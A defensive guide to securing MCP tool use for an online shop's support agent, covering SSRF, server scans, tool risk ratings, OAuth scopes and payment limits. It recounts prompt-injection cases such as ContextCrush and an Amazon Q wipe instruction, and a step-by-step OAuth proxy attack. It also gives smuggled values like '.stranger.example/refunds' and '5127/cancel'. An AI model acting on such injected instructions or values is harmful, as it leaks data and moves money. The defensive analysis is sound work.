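A server that fetches web pages sends its requests from inside its operator's network, so it may reach databases and administration pages that are closed to the public. Many cloud machines can also reach a metadata service at a fixed internal address, which may return the machine's credentials. If the server fetches any address it receives, a caller can use it to contact these systems. This attack is called *server-side request forgery* (SSRF).

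*Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) reports a case in epwforge, a document-processing server whose fetching tool accepted any address. A request to the cloud metadata address took 11.9 seconds, while a baseline request took 0.3. The delay suggests that the server tried to connect, but Padilla retrieved no reply, so the test doesn't prove that credentials were available. The fix restricted the tool to approved domains. An individual internet draft by Mohiuddin (June 2026) cites public reports of server-side request forgery (SSRF) in a fetching server from the MCP project's repository and in Microsoft's browser-automation server.

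A hostile server can also target the host. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* describes how such a server can give a client internal addresses while the client is finding out how to log in. A client that doesn't check those addresses will send requests to them from inside its own network.

The shop's `http_request` tool has this weakness by design, because it accepts any address. The developer therefore adds the shop's internal systems to the list of effects, including any that require no key because outsiders normally can't reach them.

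#### OX Security's claim about local servers

A host starts a local MCP server by running a command from its configuration. OX Security found that users of GPT Researcher, an AI research tool, could supply this command themselves. ITPro's *AI agents using Anthropic MCP could be a vector* reports that any operating-system command entered there would run. If no MCP server started, the program returned an error, but only after running the command.

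OX Security regards this as a design flaw in Anthropic's official MCP software kits and estimates that up to 200,000 instances are vulnerable. Its researchers ran commands on six companies' live services and obtained ten vulnerability listings for products that use MCP. Anthropic replied that it didn't consider this a valid vulnerability, because the user has to approve the change to the configuration file. It has since updated its security policy to urge caution with servers started this way. The project-wide version of Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* likewise warns that the local connection doesn't confine the program it starts.

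Anthropic and OX Security agree about what the software does but disagree about who should prevent misuse. Anthropic's reply is reasonable for a developer who enters a command on their own computer. It doesn't cover a web application that lets strangers fill in the command, and several products on OX Security's list allowed this without a login. The figure of 200,000 is an estimate, not a count of tested systems, and it comes from a company that sells protection against the problem. The shop's help-desk server isn't affected because it is remote. The problem would matter if the developer added a local server and let customers or the agent edit the command that starts it.

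#### A scan of servers on the public internet

Padilla also tried to measure how common server flaws are. In July 2026, Padilla collected possible server addresses from eleven sources, including certificate records, software registries and internet-wide scanners, and sent each one an MCP request to check for a correct response. Four runs over ten days confirmed 640 different servers. Padilla then tested 414 of them with software that inspected their tool descriptions, sent controlled versions of known attacks, and watched for revealing errors, delays or changes in reply size.

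After checking the strongest results by hand, Padilla reported 68 flaws to the servers' maintainers. One was in a document-search tool that inserted the user's search text into a database query without checking it. At most 16% of the servers tested had a confirmed flaw, since some may have had more than one. The software also flagged 38 servers for command injection and 29 for SSRF, but the paper presents these counts as estimates.

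The paper reports that 91.8% of the tested servers lacked OAuth, a standard way to give a program limited access to a service. In places it describes all of these servers as unauthenticated, but some used other credentials, such as fixed tokens or API keys. In the third run, Padilla found that 106 of 464 servers (23%) exposed tools without requiring any credential. The paper also states that testing covered only servers that anyone could reach without authentication, which would leave out better-protected ones.

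Of the 464 servers in the third run, 193 were unreachable three days later, so a review of a server can soon be out of date.

Padilla worked alone, and nobody has yet repeated the scan. An earlier study, also summarised in *Evaluating a Layered Prompt-Injection Defence for the Model Context Protocol*, ran a general code analyser on 583 servers and found vulnerabilities in 7.2% of them. The two studies used different methods on different sets of servers, so their results don't show that the problem has grown.

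### Match the measures to the causes

All four causes apply to the shop. Its model can err, its tickets come from strangers, and its help-desk server runs code that the developer can't inspect. The next step, rating the tools, doesn't stop any calls but shows which ones need the most protection. The later measures address the causes to different degrees:

| Measure | Model error | Injected text | Hostile or changed server | Flawed server |
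|---|---|---|---|---|
| Narrow tools and limited credentials | Remove operations the task doesn't need | Leave the attacker fewer operations to trigger | Limit what the server can do with the shop's token | Limit what an attacker can do through the server |
| Destination allowlist | Blocks requests to unintended addresses | Blocks direct requests to an attacker's address | Doesn't control requests from the operator's machines | Blocks internal addresses if it applies where the server runs |
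| Rules for each tool | Refuse amounts or arguments outside set limits | Apply the same limits whatever the ticket contains | Can catch changed descriptions, but not hidden changes in behaviour | Can refuse some dangerous arguments |
| Human approval | Catches mistakes the reviewer can recognise | Helps if the reviewer sees the full arguments | Doesn't reveal what the server does after approval | Helps little if the dangerous argument looks ordinary |
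| Testing and recovery | Find recurring mistakes and undo some effects | Test known attacks and undo some effects | Can't recover data that the operator has copied | Find known flaws and restore the shop's own data |

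## Rate each tool by its possible effects

The shop's list of effects started from credentials, because a key permits the same operations whichever tool uses it. The developer also has to rate the tools to decide what to limit first, because several tools may share one key and the agent may have tools that nobody meant it to use.

Many organisations would struggle to list their MCP servers. Pluto Security's *The MCP Debrief* reports that the median organisation has 288 different ones, and that people install most of them once and never review them again. The figure comes from a security vendor and may not hold for organisations in general, but even a tenth of that number would be too many to track from memory.

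### Make an inventory

The developer makes one entry for each tool:

1. Request the tool list from each running server, using the agent's own credential, and add any tools built into the host, such as a command line. Include the tools that the agent has no reason to call. The model sees them too, so a mistake or a planted instruction can trigger them.
2. Record what the tool changes and in whose system. If it has several modes, such as reading and deleting files, list each mode and rate the tool by the worst one.
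3. Record who could undo the change, how, and until when. With a 48-hour grace period, a deletion on Friday evening has become permanent by Monday morning.
4. Estimate the largest loss from one call, in money or in people affected. Use the limit that the receiving service enforces, which may be far above what the agent usually sends.
5. Check whether any argument takes a free-form address, database query, command or piece of code. If one does, the tool can do much more than its name suggests.
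6. Mark whether the tool reads private data, whether it returns text that outsiders wrote, and whether it can send information out of the organisation. Then list the other tools available in the same session.
7. Note who runs the server, and save a dated copy of its tool list to compare with later ones.

The list of tools should come from the running server because a scan of its source code can miss some. *1.384 herramientas MCP analizadas* (Blanco, 2026) describes a source code scan that found no tools on three servers, one of them for Excel files. Those servers do have tools, but they register them through their own frameworks, which the scanner didn't recognise.

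For the last step, Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path* reports that OX Security recommends asking who controls a tool, whether anyone can verify the code it runs, and whether the customer will know when that code changes. In the shop's case, the help-desk company controls the help desk's server, nobody can verify the code it runs, and the shop won't know when that code changes.

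A generic tool gets the same rating as the most harmful operation its credential permits. To rate `http_request`, the developer checks the payment company's API documentation for the most harmful operation the key allows. If the documentation doesn't make the key's limits clear, it is safest to assume there are none, as PocketOS found with its token. The rating doesn't improve if the agent has only issued refunds so far, because the host would also send a payout request if the agent made one.

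The shop uses three levels:

- Low: one wrong call changes nothing, or the shop can reverse the change itself at little cost.
- Medium: the shop may be unable to reverse the effect, but it stays within one order or one customer.
- High: the shop may be unable to reverse the effect, and it reaches many customers or threatens the business.

Another organisation might define the levels differently, for example by setting a sum of money for each one. The levels apply to a single call, so a tool rated medium can still cause a large loss if an agent calls it in a loop. The tool's entry should therefore include any limit on the number of calls.

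### What MCP annotations tell a client

An MCP server can supply part of this inventory itself. Since March 2025, the protocol has let servers attach annotations to their tools, including four yes-or-no hints about behaviour. Model Context Protocol's blog post on annotations lists a default for each hint and a decision that the client can base on it:

| Hint | Question it answers | Default | Example of a client's decision |
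|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Does the tool leave its environment unchanged? | No | Skip the confirmation if yes |
| `destructiveHint` | Can its changes destroy something, rather than only add to it? | Yes | Show a warning before the call if yes |
| `idempotentHint` | Is it safe to repeat the call with the same arguments? | No | Retry after a failure if yes |
| `openWorldHint` | Does it deal with outside entities, rather than a closed set of data? | Yes | Check the output for untrusted content if yes |

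If a tool has no annotations, the client should by default treat it as one that makes destructive changes, can't safely run twice and deals with the outside world. Many servers omit annotations, and clients differ in how strictly they apply these defaults. A strict client may ask for confirmation before an unannotated weather lookup, and a lax one may send an unannotated payment without asking.

Even accurate hints can leave out risks. A refund only adds a record to the payment company's books, so a server's author could honestly set `destructiveHint` to false, even though the money may be impossible to recover. The help-desk company could reasonably describe its ticket database as a closed set of data, but strangers wrote the tickets in it. Accurate hints for the shop's `http_request` would match the defaults and apply to every call, so they couldn't help a client tell an order lookup from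 a payout.

### The dispute over hints that may be false

A malicious server can mark a tool as read-only and still delete files when the agent calls it. During review of the original proposal for tool annotations, MCP co-creator Justin Spahr-Summers wrote that the information would be very useful if clients could trust it, but wondered how a client could use a flag "knowing that it's not trustable". Another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, argued that clients should ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, even the display title.

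The project compromised by calling every annotation a hint. Clients must treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, and each client decides how much weight to give them. Model Context Protocol's *Record Class McpSchema.ToolAnnotations*, a reference page for Java developers, is stricter and tells clients never to base decisions about tool use on annotations from untrusted servers.

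Hosmer's position is the safer one for any hint that would relax a check. If a client skips the confirmation because an unknown server marked its tool as read-only, the server's operator has in effect switched off the client's protection. If the server instead marks a tool as destructive, the worst result of trusting that hint is a little time lost to an unnecessary warning. The shop can let any server's hints raise a tool's rating, but let them lower it only if the shop trusts the operator and has checked the tool itself.

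Annotations are most useful when one organisation runs both the client and the server, as many large companies do internally. Few products make much use of them so far. According to Model Context Protocol's post, most clients trust a server once it is installed and draw no further distinctions. None of them let users filter tools by annotation. The closest equivalent in production was GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of its users had switched on. The post recommends using annotations as one input to a client's rules, and relying on network controls or a sandbox (an isolated environment for running code) where a guarantee is needed.

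### Proposals for richer annotations

Model Context Protocol (2026) describes additional hints that would fill some of the gaps. A `reversibleHint` would distinguish moving a file to the trash from deleting it permanently. An `egressHint` would mark tools that can send data out. Currently, `openWorldHint` covers both these tools and tools that bring in untrusted text.

A more ambitious proposal, SEP-1913, comes from developers at GitHub and OpenAI who ran into these gaps in production. It would also annotate the results that tools return. A session's sensitivity could then rise but never fall. For example, if the shop's agent read a ticket with a home address, the host would treat the session as sensitive from then on and could hold any later message to an outside recipient.

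SEP-1862 deals with tools that have several modes. Before a call, the client would send the server the intended arguments and receive annotations for that call, so a file tool could be marked read-only when reading and destructive when deleting. This would help with generic tools on a trusted server. An untrusted server could still return false annotations, and it would receive the arguments before anyone had approved the call.

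Progress has been slow, and in mid-July Model Context Protocol still listed both SEP-1862 and SEP-1913 as drafts. The project has formed an interest group on annotations, whose charter, dated 20 April 2026, refers to six separate proposals. The group can only make recommendations. For a change to the specification, a working group normally sponsors the proposal and the project's core maintainers decide on it. The interest group's participants include Microsoft, OpenAI and Anthropic, which build both hosts and servers and so have a commercial reason to want hints that other companies' products will follow.

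Chrome's WebMCP, a related system that lets websites offer tools to visiting agents, already has a label of this kind. Search Engine Journal's *The WebMCP Tools You Expose To Agents Can Be Used To Hijack* explains that a site can attach `untrustedContentHint` to a tool that returns customer reviews or comments. An honest help desk can't properly describe its tickets with the four MCP hints, so it could use a label like this one.

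### Why the combination of tools matters

A tool that searches emails can't leak anything if the agent has no way to send information out. If the agent also has a tool that posts to a website, a planted instruction can make it search for a password and publish it. This danger comes from the combination of tools, so it wouldn't show up if each tool were rated separately.

The programmer Simon Willison uses the term *lethal trifecta* for the dangerous combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate with the outside. An attacker can place instructions in the untrusted content that tell the model to send them the private data. Users can easily create this combination by accident with MCP, because they routinely connect several servers to one session. Each server's operator knows only that server's tools, so only the host's developer can check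 for the combination.

Help Net Security's *One in four MCP servers opens AI agent security to code execution* describes an attack of this type called ContextCrush. A developer asked the coding agent Cursor for help, and the agent fetched documentation that an attacker had altered. The documentation contained hidden instructions to read files on the developer's computer and paste their contents into a GitHub issue that the attacker controlled. The developer saw only ordinary coding help.

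The trifecta covers data theft, but an attacker who wants a refund doesn't need to read anything private. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* accounts for this. It says an agent becomes dangerous when it combines untrusted input, access to sensitive data, and the ability to change something or communicate externally, so developers should allow it at most two of these.

Security Boulevard's *The Half of Agent Security You're Not Governing* (2026) argues that the rule has failed in real incidents. In July 2025, an attacker planted an instruction in the Amazon Q coding extension that told the agent to wipe the user's files and cloud resources. Security Boulevard counts only two of the three conditions because the attack involved no outside communication. That count is doubtful because the third condition also includes making changes, and an agent that can wipe someone's files and cloud resources presumably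 has access to sensitive data as well.

In the stronger example, from the same month, a coding agent from Replit destroyed a production database holding more than 1,200 executives' records, and no attacker was involved. The rule is meant to limit prompt injection, so it doesn't protect against an agent that makes such a mistake on its own.

The developer should therefore use the inventory to check each session for two risks. If the session's tools together provide private data, outsiders' text and a way to send information out, the developer should assume that an outsider could obtain any data the tools can read. If the session contains outsiders' text and a tool with a high rating, the developer should assume that an outsider could trigger that tool's worst call. Even in a session that passes both checks, an agent could do great damage by calling a tool by mistake, so each tool still needs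 its own rating.

### What studies show about the tools in use

Published counts give some idea of how often these tools and combinations occur, though most come from companies that sell protection against them.

The broadest study is Stein's, cited earlier for its finding that tools for making changes rose from 27% to 65% of use. Stein searched GitHub and Smithery, a registry of MCP servers, and narrowed 73,338 candidates to 19,388 verified servers. A language model then classified each tool. Fourteen people with advanced degrees in machine learning checked 100 tools each and agreed with the model 81% of the time on whether a tool reads, analyses or changes something.

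Only 36% of the published tools make changes, so their much larger share of use reflects which servers people download. Stein had download figures for 3,854 servers and counted each installation as one use of every tool on the server. The figures mostly leave out remote servers, which users don't need to download, and Stein cautions that they may mainly show what developers are trying out. The trend towards tools that make changes is probably real, but the 65% figure is based on downloads and doesn't measure how many of agents' calls change something.

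Stein also counted public servers with payment tools and found that their number rose from 47 in January 2025 to 1,578 in February 2026. That is about a 34-fold increase, compared with about 36-fold for public tools of all kinds, so payment servers seem to have grown roughly in line with the general trend. Stein works at the UK AI Security Institute, a government body, and carried out the monitoring in collaboration with the Bank of England. The paper recommends this kind of monitoring to regulators, so Stein has an interest in promoting the method but is not selling a product.

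Noma Security, which sells protection for AI agents, analysed hundreds of popular MCP servers and *skills* (written instructions that an agent loads). According to Security Boulevard, Noma found that 76% of servers in organisations had high-risk capabilities and 60% could change data or the state of a system. One in four popular servers could run arbitrary code. A single tool is enough to put a server in one of these categories, so the 60% of servers isn't comparable with Stein's 36% of tools. Help Net Security reports that half of the servers able to communicate externally also had untrusted input and sensitive data in the same set of tools, so connecting to just one of them gives an agent the whole trifecta.

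Servers that handle money often have other dangerous tools. PolicyLayer (2026), a vendor's report from May, found 60 servers with financial tools, of which 28 (46.7%) could also destroy data. A later edition found 783 such servers, of which 58.5% could. The count probably rose thirteenfold more because the dataset grew than because new servers appeared, so neither percentage is a reliable estimate for the whole market. Both are high enough that the shop should read the full tool list before connecting to a payment company's server, even if it only needs refunds.

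A developer published the scan that Blanco describes on dev.to in October 2026. It covered 1,384 tools on 28 servers written in Python and used the open-source program AgentSploit to look for *sources*, which bring in outside content, and *sinks*, which act on something. It found 239 sources, 384 sinks and 59 tools that were both. Fourteen of the 28 servers would give an agent both sources and sinks with no warning about the combination.

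The program classified tools largely by their names and arguments. A tool counted as a source if its name was a word like "search", and as a sink if it took an argument like "query". An ordinary search tool that takes a query is therefore both, so some of the 59 may be harmless. The scan is better evidence that sources and sinks commonly occur together than that any particular tool is dangerous. Blanco's account appeared on the blog of Donweb, a hosting company.

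The same scan searched tool descriptions for hidden instructions and flagged nine. The developer read all nine and found only legitimate usage notes, such as an instruction to call one tool before another. An honest author and an attacker can write the same instruction, so someone at the shop has to read the descriptions.

### The shop's ratings

The developer requests the help desk's tool list and finds four tools. The agent uses three of them, to read a ticket, search old tickets and reply to a customer. The fourth, `message_all_customers`, sends an announcement to everyone who has ever written to the shop. The developer missed this effect in the earlier list because they had considered only what the agent used the server for.

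| Tool | Worst single call | Can the shop undo it? | Free-form address, query or code? | Role in a data leak | Rating |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `get_ticket` | Read one customer's details | Nothing to undo | No | Private data, outsiders' text | Low |
| `search_tickets` | Read many customers' details | Nothing to undo | Search text only | Private data, outsiders' text | Low |
| `reply_to_ticket` | Send one customer another's details | No | No | Sends information out | Medium |
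| `message_all_customers` (unused) | Send private details or a false notice to every customer | No | No | Sends information out | High |
| `http_request` | Pay out the $80,000 balance, or delete the order database and its backups | Probably not the payout; the deletion only with a grace period or a separate copy | Address, method and body | All three | High |

`http_request` has one row, although it reaches several companies, because the agent gets all of the tool's uses together. Individually, restarting the web service would be rated low and a single refund would be rated medium.

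The session fails both checks, so the developer has to assume that a stranger's ticket could trigger a payout or a message to every customer. Removing `http_request` would prevent the payout, but private data could still leak because the help desk's own tools complete the trifecta. An attacker could send a ticket asking for the delivery address on someone else's order, and the agent could find the address with `search_tickets` and send it back with `reply_to_ticket`. The agent needs both tools for its ordinary work.

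## Replace general tools with narrow ones and limit their credentials

The shop's agent has two tools rated high, `http_request` and `message_all_customers`. Before adding any checks, the developer can reduce the danger by limiting what each tool lets the model request and what its credential permits. The shop needs both changes. Restricting the payment key wouldn't stop `http_request` from sending a customer's address to a stranger's server, because that request needs no key. And a narrow refund tool wouldn't prevent a payout if the agent found the full payment key elsewhere, as PocketOS's agent found a hosting token in an unrelated file.

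### Four designs for a tool that calls an API

The shop's `http_request` tool can send any request to any address. The developer writes it once, and it works with every web service, including ones nobody planned to use. It takes up one entry in the tool list.

A more limited tool accepts any request under one base address, such as `api.payments.example`. The developer needs one for each service but doesn't have to update it when the service adds an operation. The model can't use it to contact other servers, but it can still request a payout. meinGPT's *HTTP API (Generic)* describes a tool of this kind for AI assistants that also lets an administrator allow only certain paths, such as `/v1`, and block others, such as `/admin`.

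The tool's code has to enforce the base address carefully. The sample code in Cloudflare's *Build a search and execute MCP server* checks that a path from the model starts with a slash before joining it to the base address. Without that check, the model could supply `.stranger.example/refunds` as the path. The full address would then be `api.example.com.stranger.example/refunds`, which belongs to a stranger, and the code would send the credential there.

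A developer can also divide a tool by risk. meinGPT's tool has separate methods for reading, writing and dangerous requests, so an administrator can allow reading and restrict the rest. Someone has to assign each operation to a group, and the HTTP method isn't enough to determine which one, as Railway's API shows. The groups can also be too broad, since a refund and a change of bank account are both writes.

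The narrowest kind of tool performs one fixed operation, like `refund_order`. A developer has to write and maintain each tool, and a customer with an unusual request has to wait for staff. An argument can still sometimes change the operation. Docker's API tool inserts arguments into the web address as plain text and leaves encoding to the developer. If the address ended in `/orders/${order}`, an order number of `5127/cancel` could turn a lookup into a cancellation. The developer can prevent this by encoding the value or accepting only digits.

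meinGPT also offers request templates, which look like fixed operations. But the model can override a template's query, headers and body, so a refund template wouldn't fix the details of the refund.

| Design | Coverage | Upkeep | Tool list | What a wrong call can still do |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any request to any address | Every web service | Almost none | One entry | Anything the agent's keys permit, or send data to a stranger |
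| Any request under one base address | One service's whole API | Little, as new operations work at once | One entry per service | Anything the key permits at that service |
| Separate read, write and dangerous methods | One service's whole API | Somebody classifies each new operation | Three entries per service | Anything in the groups that the agent may use |
| One fixed operation | Only what the developer planned | A developer updates each tool | One entry per operation | That operation, with wrong arguments |

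### The case for general tools

Narrow tools work badly for an agent whose tasks are hard to predict. An engineer's agent that investigates outages might need any of several hundred operations. The model usually reads the description of every available tool before it starts, which costs money and leaves less room for the task. Developers measure this cost in tokens, the short pieces of text that a model processes. (These have nothing to do with access tokens.)

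Cloudflare's API has more than 2,500 operations. Cloudflare calculates that an MCP server with a separate tool for each would need about 1.17 million tokens for tool descriptions, or about 244,000 if the descriptions listed only required arguments. Cloudflare's own MCP server needs about 1,000 because it covers the whole API with two main tools, `search` and `execute`. The model writes a short program to search the API's documentation, then another to call the operations it finds.

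In *Code Mode*, Carey describes a user who asks for protection against a flood of hostile traffic. The agent found the relevant operations and inspected the current settings in four tool calls. A program can also filter a long reply so the model reads only what it needs. When Cloudflare adds a product, the agent can use it without anyone writing a new tool. Carey argues that hand-maintained servers could not keep up with an API of this size, which seems right.

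Cloudflare runs the model's programs in an isolated environment with no files or environment variables, and they can't contact outside addresses directly unless a developer allows it. When users connect, they choose which permissions to grant, and the server's access token carries only those. According to Cloudflare's *Code Mode MCP server patterns*, each program receives a function for sending authenticated requests but never the credential.

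These safeguards protect the credential and the machine, but a program can still make any change the user's permissions allow. It can also make a dozen changes in one `execute` call, which a host would record as a single tool call. Cloudflare warns that "code execution does not replace authorization". Its software for building similar servers doesn't provide lasting approval for each request inside `execute`, so the developer has to enforce permissions in the code that sends the requests. Cloudflare describes Code Mode as experimental.

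This design suits the engineer's agent, especially with read-only permissions. The shop needs it much less. Cloudflare's figures work out to about 450 tokens per fully described tool, so six narrow tools would take up roughly 2,700. A client can also shorten a long tool list. OpenAI's `allowed_tools` setting imports only the tools the developer names. Its `defer_loading` setting saves tokens by loading descriptions only when the model needs them, but it doesn't remove any tools.

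### Limit what the credential permits

A program that uses OAuth gets its access token from an *authorization server*, which first asks the user for consent. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) sets out how remote MCP servers should use OAuth, but makes authorization optional, so the shop has to check what each server supports.

#### Scopes

A credential's *scope* is the set of operations it permits. OAuth also uses "scope" for each named permission, such as `files:read`. A client should start with as few scopes as possible. If an operation needs another scope, the server refuses the request and names the missing scope. The client can then ask for a new token, a process MCP calls *step-up authorization*. The client normally asks for its old scopes plus the new one, so an agent's permissions tend to grow over time. A client that acts on its own behalf may abandon the request instead,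 which is the better choice for the shop's agent because it runs with nobody watching.

A carelessly configured server can cause a client to request far more access than it needs. If the server doesn't say which scopes an operation needs, the client requests every scope on the server's published list. Under the protocol, that list should contain only basic scopes, but Model Context Protocol describes publishing every possible scope as a common mistake. Whoever connects the server should read the consent page rather than assume that the client has requested the minimum.

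Some services don't offer a scope as narrow as the tool. In OpenAI's older built-in connector for Gmail, the tools that search and read email require the `gmail.modify` scope. The equivalent tools for Outlook need only `Mail.Read`. An agent with the Gmail tools may be unable to change an email, but someone who stole its token could change one.

When a token lacks a required scope, existing data can also appear to be missing. According to Glama's *Cloudflare MCP Server*, some Cloudflare operations return an empty list when the token lacks permission. An agent could wrongly conclude that an account has no websites and set them up again. Cloudflare's MCP server now treats such a reply as a refusal.

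#### Short lifetimes and separate test accounts

The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) recommends short-lived access tokens, which give a thief less time to use a stolen one. Short lifetimes don't protect against the agent's own mistakes, because the agent acts with a valid token. The client may hold a *refresh token*, which it exchanges for new access tokens. A thief who also steals the refresh token may be able to keep renewing access, so the host has to protect it at least as carefully as the access token.

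Cancelling a token may not take effect immediately. *A platform team's guide to MCP 7-28* (Körbächer, 2026) explains that a server can save the result of a token check to avoid repeating it for every request. If the server keeps the result for 60 seconds, a cancelled token can keep working for up to 60 more seconds, which is long enough for an agent in a loop to make many refunds.

Test agents need their own credentials, which shouldn't work on production accounts. *Treasury for agents*, from the payment company Stripe, says users who connect a client to Stripe's MCP server through OAuth can choose particular live accounts or sandboxes and set different permissions for each. A developer can therefore let an agent try payouts in a sandbox without giving it access to real money.

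#### Tokens for one server only

A token's *audience* is the server that should accept it. An MCP client must name that server in the `resource` field when it requests a token, and the server must reject tokens issued for other servers. If the help-desk company tried to use the shop's token at another company's MCP server, that server should reject it. WorkOS (2026) notes that the field has been compulsory since June 2025, although many guides still omit it.

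This protection also depends on the authorization server. A client has to send the field even to an authorization server that doesn't support it, and that server may issue a token that isn't tied to one audience. A developer can test this by sending one MCP server's token to another. An ordinary API key often has no such restriction, so any server that receives the key can use it directly with the service that issued it.

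#### Secrets outside the model's reach

The host should add credentials after the model has written its request, as the shop's host already does, so they never enter the model's context. OpenAI's service doesn't store the access token for a remote MCP server, so the developer's application has to send it with every request.

A key can still reach the model by other routes. Docker warns that keys in request headers are visible in debug logs, so an agent with a tool for reading logs could find them. An agent with a command line may be able to print any keys stored in the host's environment variables. Cloudflare advises developers to keep secrets out of API documentation and results, since the model's programs can read both. MCP bans access tokens in URL query strings, which often end up in server logs.

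### When a server misuses its own authority

A server often has more authority than the people who call it. The help-desk company's server, for example, might use one key to read the tickets of every business it serves. Suppose a rival shop with a valid account asks for one of this shop's tickets. If the server checks only that the rival's token is valid, it will use its own key to fetch the ticket. This is called the *confused deputy* problem. To prevent it, the server has to check that the caller is allowed to read that particular ticket.

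Model Context Protocol describes a version of this attack that exploits the login process. A *proxy server* connects many MCP clients to another company's API, such as a file storage service. The storage service knows the proxy by a single identifier, whichever client is using it. The attack then works like this:

1. A user connects through the proxy and approves its access on the storage service's consent page. The service saves a cookie in the user's browser to remember the approval.
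2. An attacker registers a program as a new client of the proxy, gives a return address on the attacker's own website, and sends the user a link.
3. The user opens the link. The storage service sees the cookie and skips the consent page.
4. The proxy receives the storage service's approval and sends a login code to the attacker's return address.
5. The attacker exchanges the code for an access token and uses the proxy to reach the user's files.

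The user approved the proxy once, for a different client, so the proxy has to show its own consent page for each new client before it contacts the storage service. The page must name the client, list the permissions and show the return address.

#### Why MCP forbids passing on a client's token

MCP forbids *token passthrough*, in which a proxy forwards each client's token to the service behind it so that the proxy needs no authority of its own. If the service accepts these tokens, a client can bypass the proxy's limits and checks by contacting the service directly. The service's logs may show the wrong source for a request, which makes an incident harder to investigate. And if the proxy doesn't check who a token was issued for, a thief can send requests through the proxy with a stolen token.

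The proxy must instead get a separate token for the service behind it. That token may permit more than the caller's does, so the proxy still has to check what each caller is allowed to do.

Cloudflare's sample server checks that the incoming request has a bearer token, then forwards the same token to the API. Cloudflare says the token never enters the environment where the model's program runs, so the program can't read it. But forwarding the token still violates MCP's authorization specification. To comply, a developer who copies the sample would need to check the token's audience and use a separate token for the API.

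#### The July 2026 authorization changes

The July 2026 revision added a defence against *mix-up attacks*, in which an attacker who controls one of a client's authorization servers tries to make the client send that server a login code issued by a legitimate one. The client must now record which authorization server it expects a response from and compare this with the `iss` field in the response before using the code. The check works only if the legitimate server includes that field, which the specification recommends but doesn't yet require. Clients also can't reuse their registration credentials with a different authorization server.

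The revision also deprecated the automatic registration that the attacker uses in step 2. Under the preferred method, a client identifies itself with the address of a web page that describes it, and Model Context Protocol says an authorization server can accept only domains it trusts. Attackers can publish such pages too, so a proxy that accepts any domain still needs a consent page for each client. The method also can't prove which program on a user's computer is receiving the login code, so a malicious local program could impersonate a trusted one.

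### Choose who runs the server

OpenAI recommends using a service provider's own MCP server where one exists, such as Stripe's at `mcp.stripe.com`. Stripe already processes its customers' payments, whereas a server run by another company lets a second company see the arguments and results of every call. That company may also hold a credential for the payment account.

Workato's *Stripe Billing Operations* describes a server of this kind. A customer can connect it to Stripe by giving Workato a Stripe API key or by approving access on Stripe's login page. A full secret key would give the server far more authority than most billing tasks need, so a customer who uses an API key should ask whether one with fewer permissions will work.

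An intermediary can still be a sensible choice if the provider has no MCP server, or if the intermediary's tools are narrower. Before connecting, the developer should ask what credential the intermediary will hold, how to cancel it, and what the company does with the data. OpenAI advises particular care with intermediaries.

A provider's own server may also offer more tools than an agent needs. In June 2025, the npm page for Stripe's server listed tools for creating refunds and coupons and for updating subscriptions and disputes. A shop whose agent only makes refunds would have to filter out the other tools and restrict the API key's permissions. It could instead write its own narrow tool that calls Stripe's API directly. This avoids involving another operator, but the shop has to maintain the code.

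### What payment controls limit

Stripe lets a business create *restricted keys*. According to Stripe's *Restricted API keys*, every permission on a new key starts at "None", and the key can replace an ordinary secret key without code changes. Stripe's *API permissions reference* says each permission allows certain requests. The developer should check whether the permission for refunds allows anything else.

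A restricted key also limits any MCP server that uses it. According to the setup instructions for Stripe's server, the key controls what the tools may do, so a tool can appear in the model's list and still fail when the agent calls it. Stripe also offers agent API keys for applications that need independent, persistent access. Because these keys are meant to last, the business needs a way to replace one quickly if it leaks.

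Permissions limit the kind of payment but not the total amount. An agent with a key that allows refunds could refund every recent order. A *spending limit*, where a payment company offers one, caps the amount over a set period but may not restrict who receives the money. An *agent-payment mandate* is a signed record of what a buyer has authorised an agent to purchase, such as one pair of shoes for less than $100. It can limit the item, the price and the time, but it is meant for purchases, so it wouldn't limit refunds.

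A payment company's own limits apply to every request made with the credential, including a thief's, while spending rules at the shop's gateway cover only the calls that pass through it.

A business can also keep less money in the account the agent uses. If the shop's refunds average $40, its 150 refunds a day come to $6,000, far less than the $80,000 in its payment account. Moving the rest elsewhere would reduce the loss from a stolen key, though refunds might fail on an unusually busy day.

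### The shop's new tools

The developer removes `http_request` and writes three narrow tools. In simplified form, the code for refunds is:

```python
def refund_order(order, amount_usd):
    payment = payments.find_payment(order)
    return payments.refund(payment.id, amount_usd)
```

The code finds the customer's original payment and refunds it. At this payment company, a refund goes back to the card or account that paid. The tool has no argument for a bank account, so the model can't send the money to anyone else.

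The shop also replaces its payment key with one that can only look up payments and create refunds. An attacker who gets this key can't use it to pay out the balance, charge a saved card or change the shop's bank account. The developer cancels the old key, since anyone who found a copy in a forgotten file could still do all three.

The model can still refund the $310 desk instead of the $40 lamp. A dishonest customer can still plant instructions in a ticket and get a refund for something they keep, although the money can now go only to the person who paid for the order. The change also makes refunds harder for honest customers who have closed their card, because the refund fails and a member of staff has to arrange another way to pay them.

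The other two tools are `restart_web_service`, which takes no arguments, and `post_staff_note`, which takes only the text of the note. The hosting company can limit a key to one service but not to one operation, so the developer creates a key that covers the web service but not the order database. The key could still delete the web service, but the tool only restarts it. The developer moves the staff chat's webhook address into the host's configuration, where the model can't see it.

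For the help desk, the developer leaves `message_all_customers` out of the agent's tool list and gets a new token with scopes only for reading and answering tickets. If the agent called the missing tool anyway, the help desk's server would refuse the request.

| Tool | What the credential permits | Worst single call through the tool | Rating |
|---|---|---|---|
| `refund_order` | Look up payments and create refunds | Refund the wrong order in full | Medium |
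| `restart_web_service` | Manage the web service, but not the database | Briefly interrupt a working website | Low |
| `post_staff_note` | Post to one staff chat | Post a false instruction that staff or an automation carry out | Medium |
| `get_ticket` | Read tickets | Read one customer's details | Low |
| `search_tickets` | Read tickets | Read many customers' details | Low |
| `reply_to_ticket` | Answer tickets | Send one customer another's details | Medium |

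The rating for staff notes assumes that staff would question an instruction affecting many orders. No tool now has a high rating, but nothing yet stops the agent from calling `refund_order` hundreds of times, and the help desk's tools still complete the lethal trifecta.

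## Restrict where requests may go

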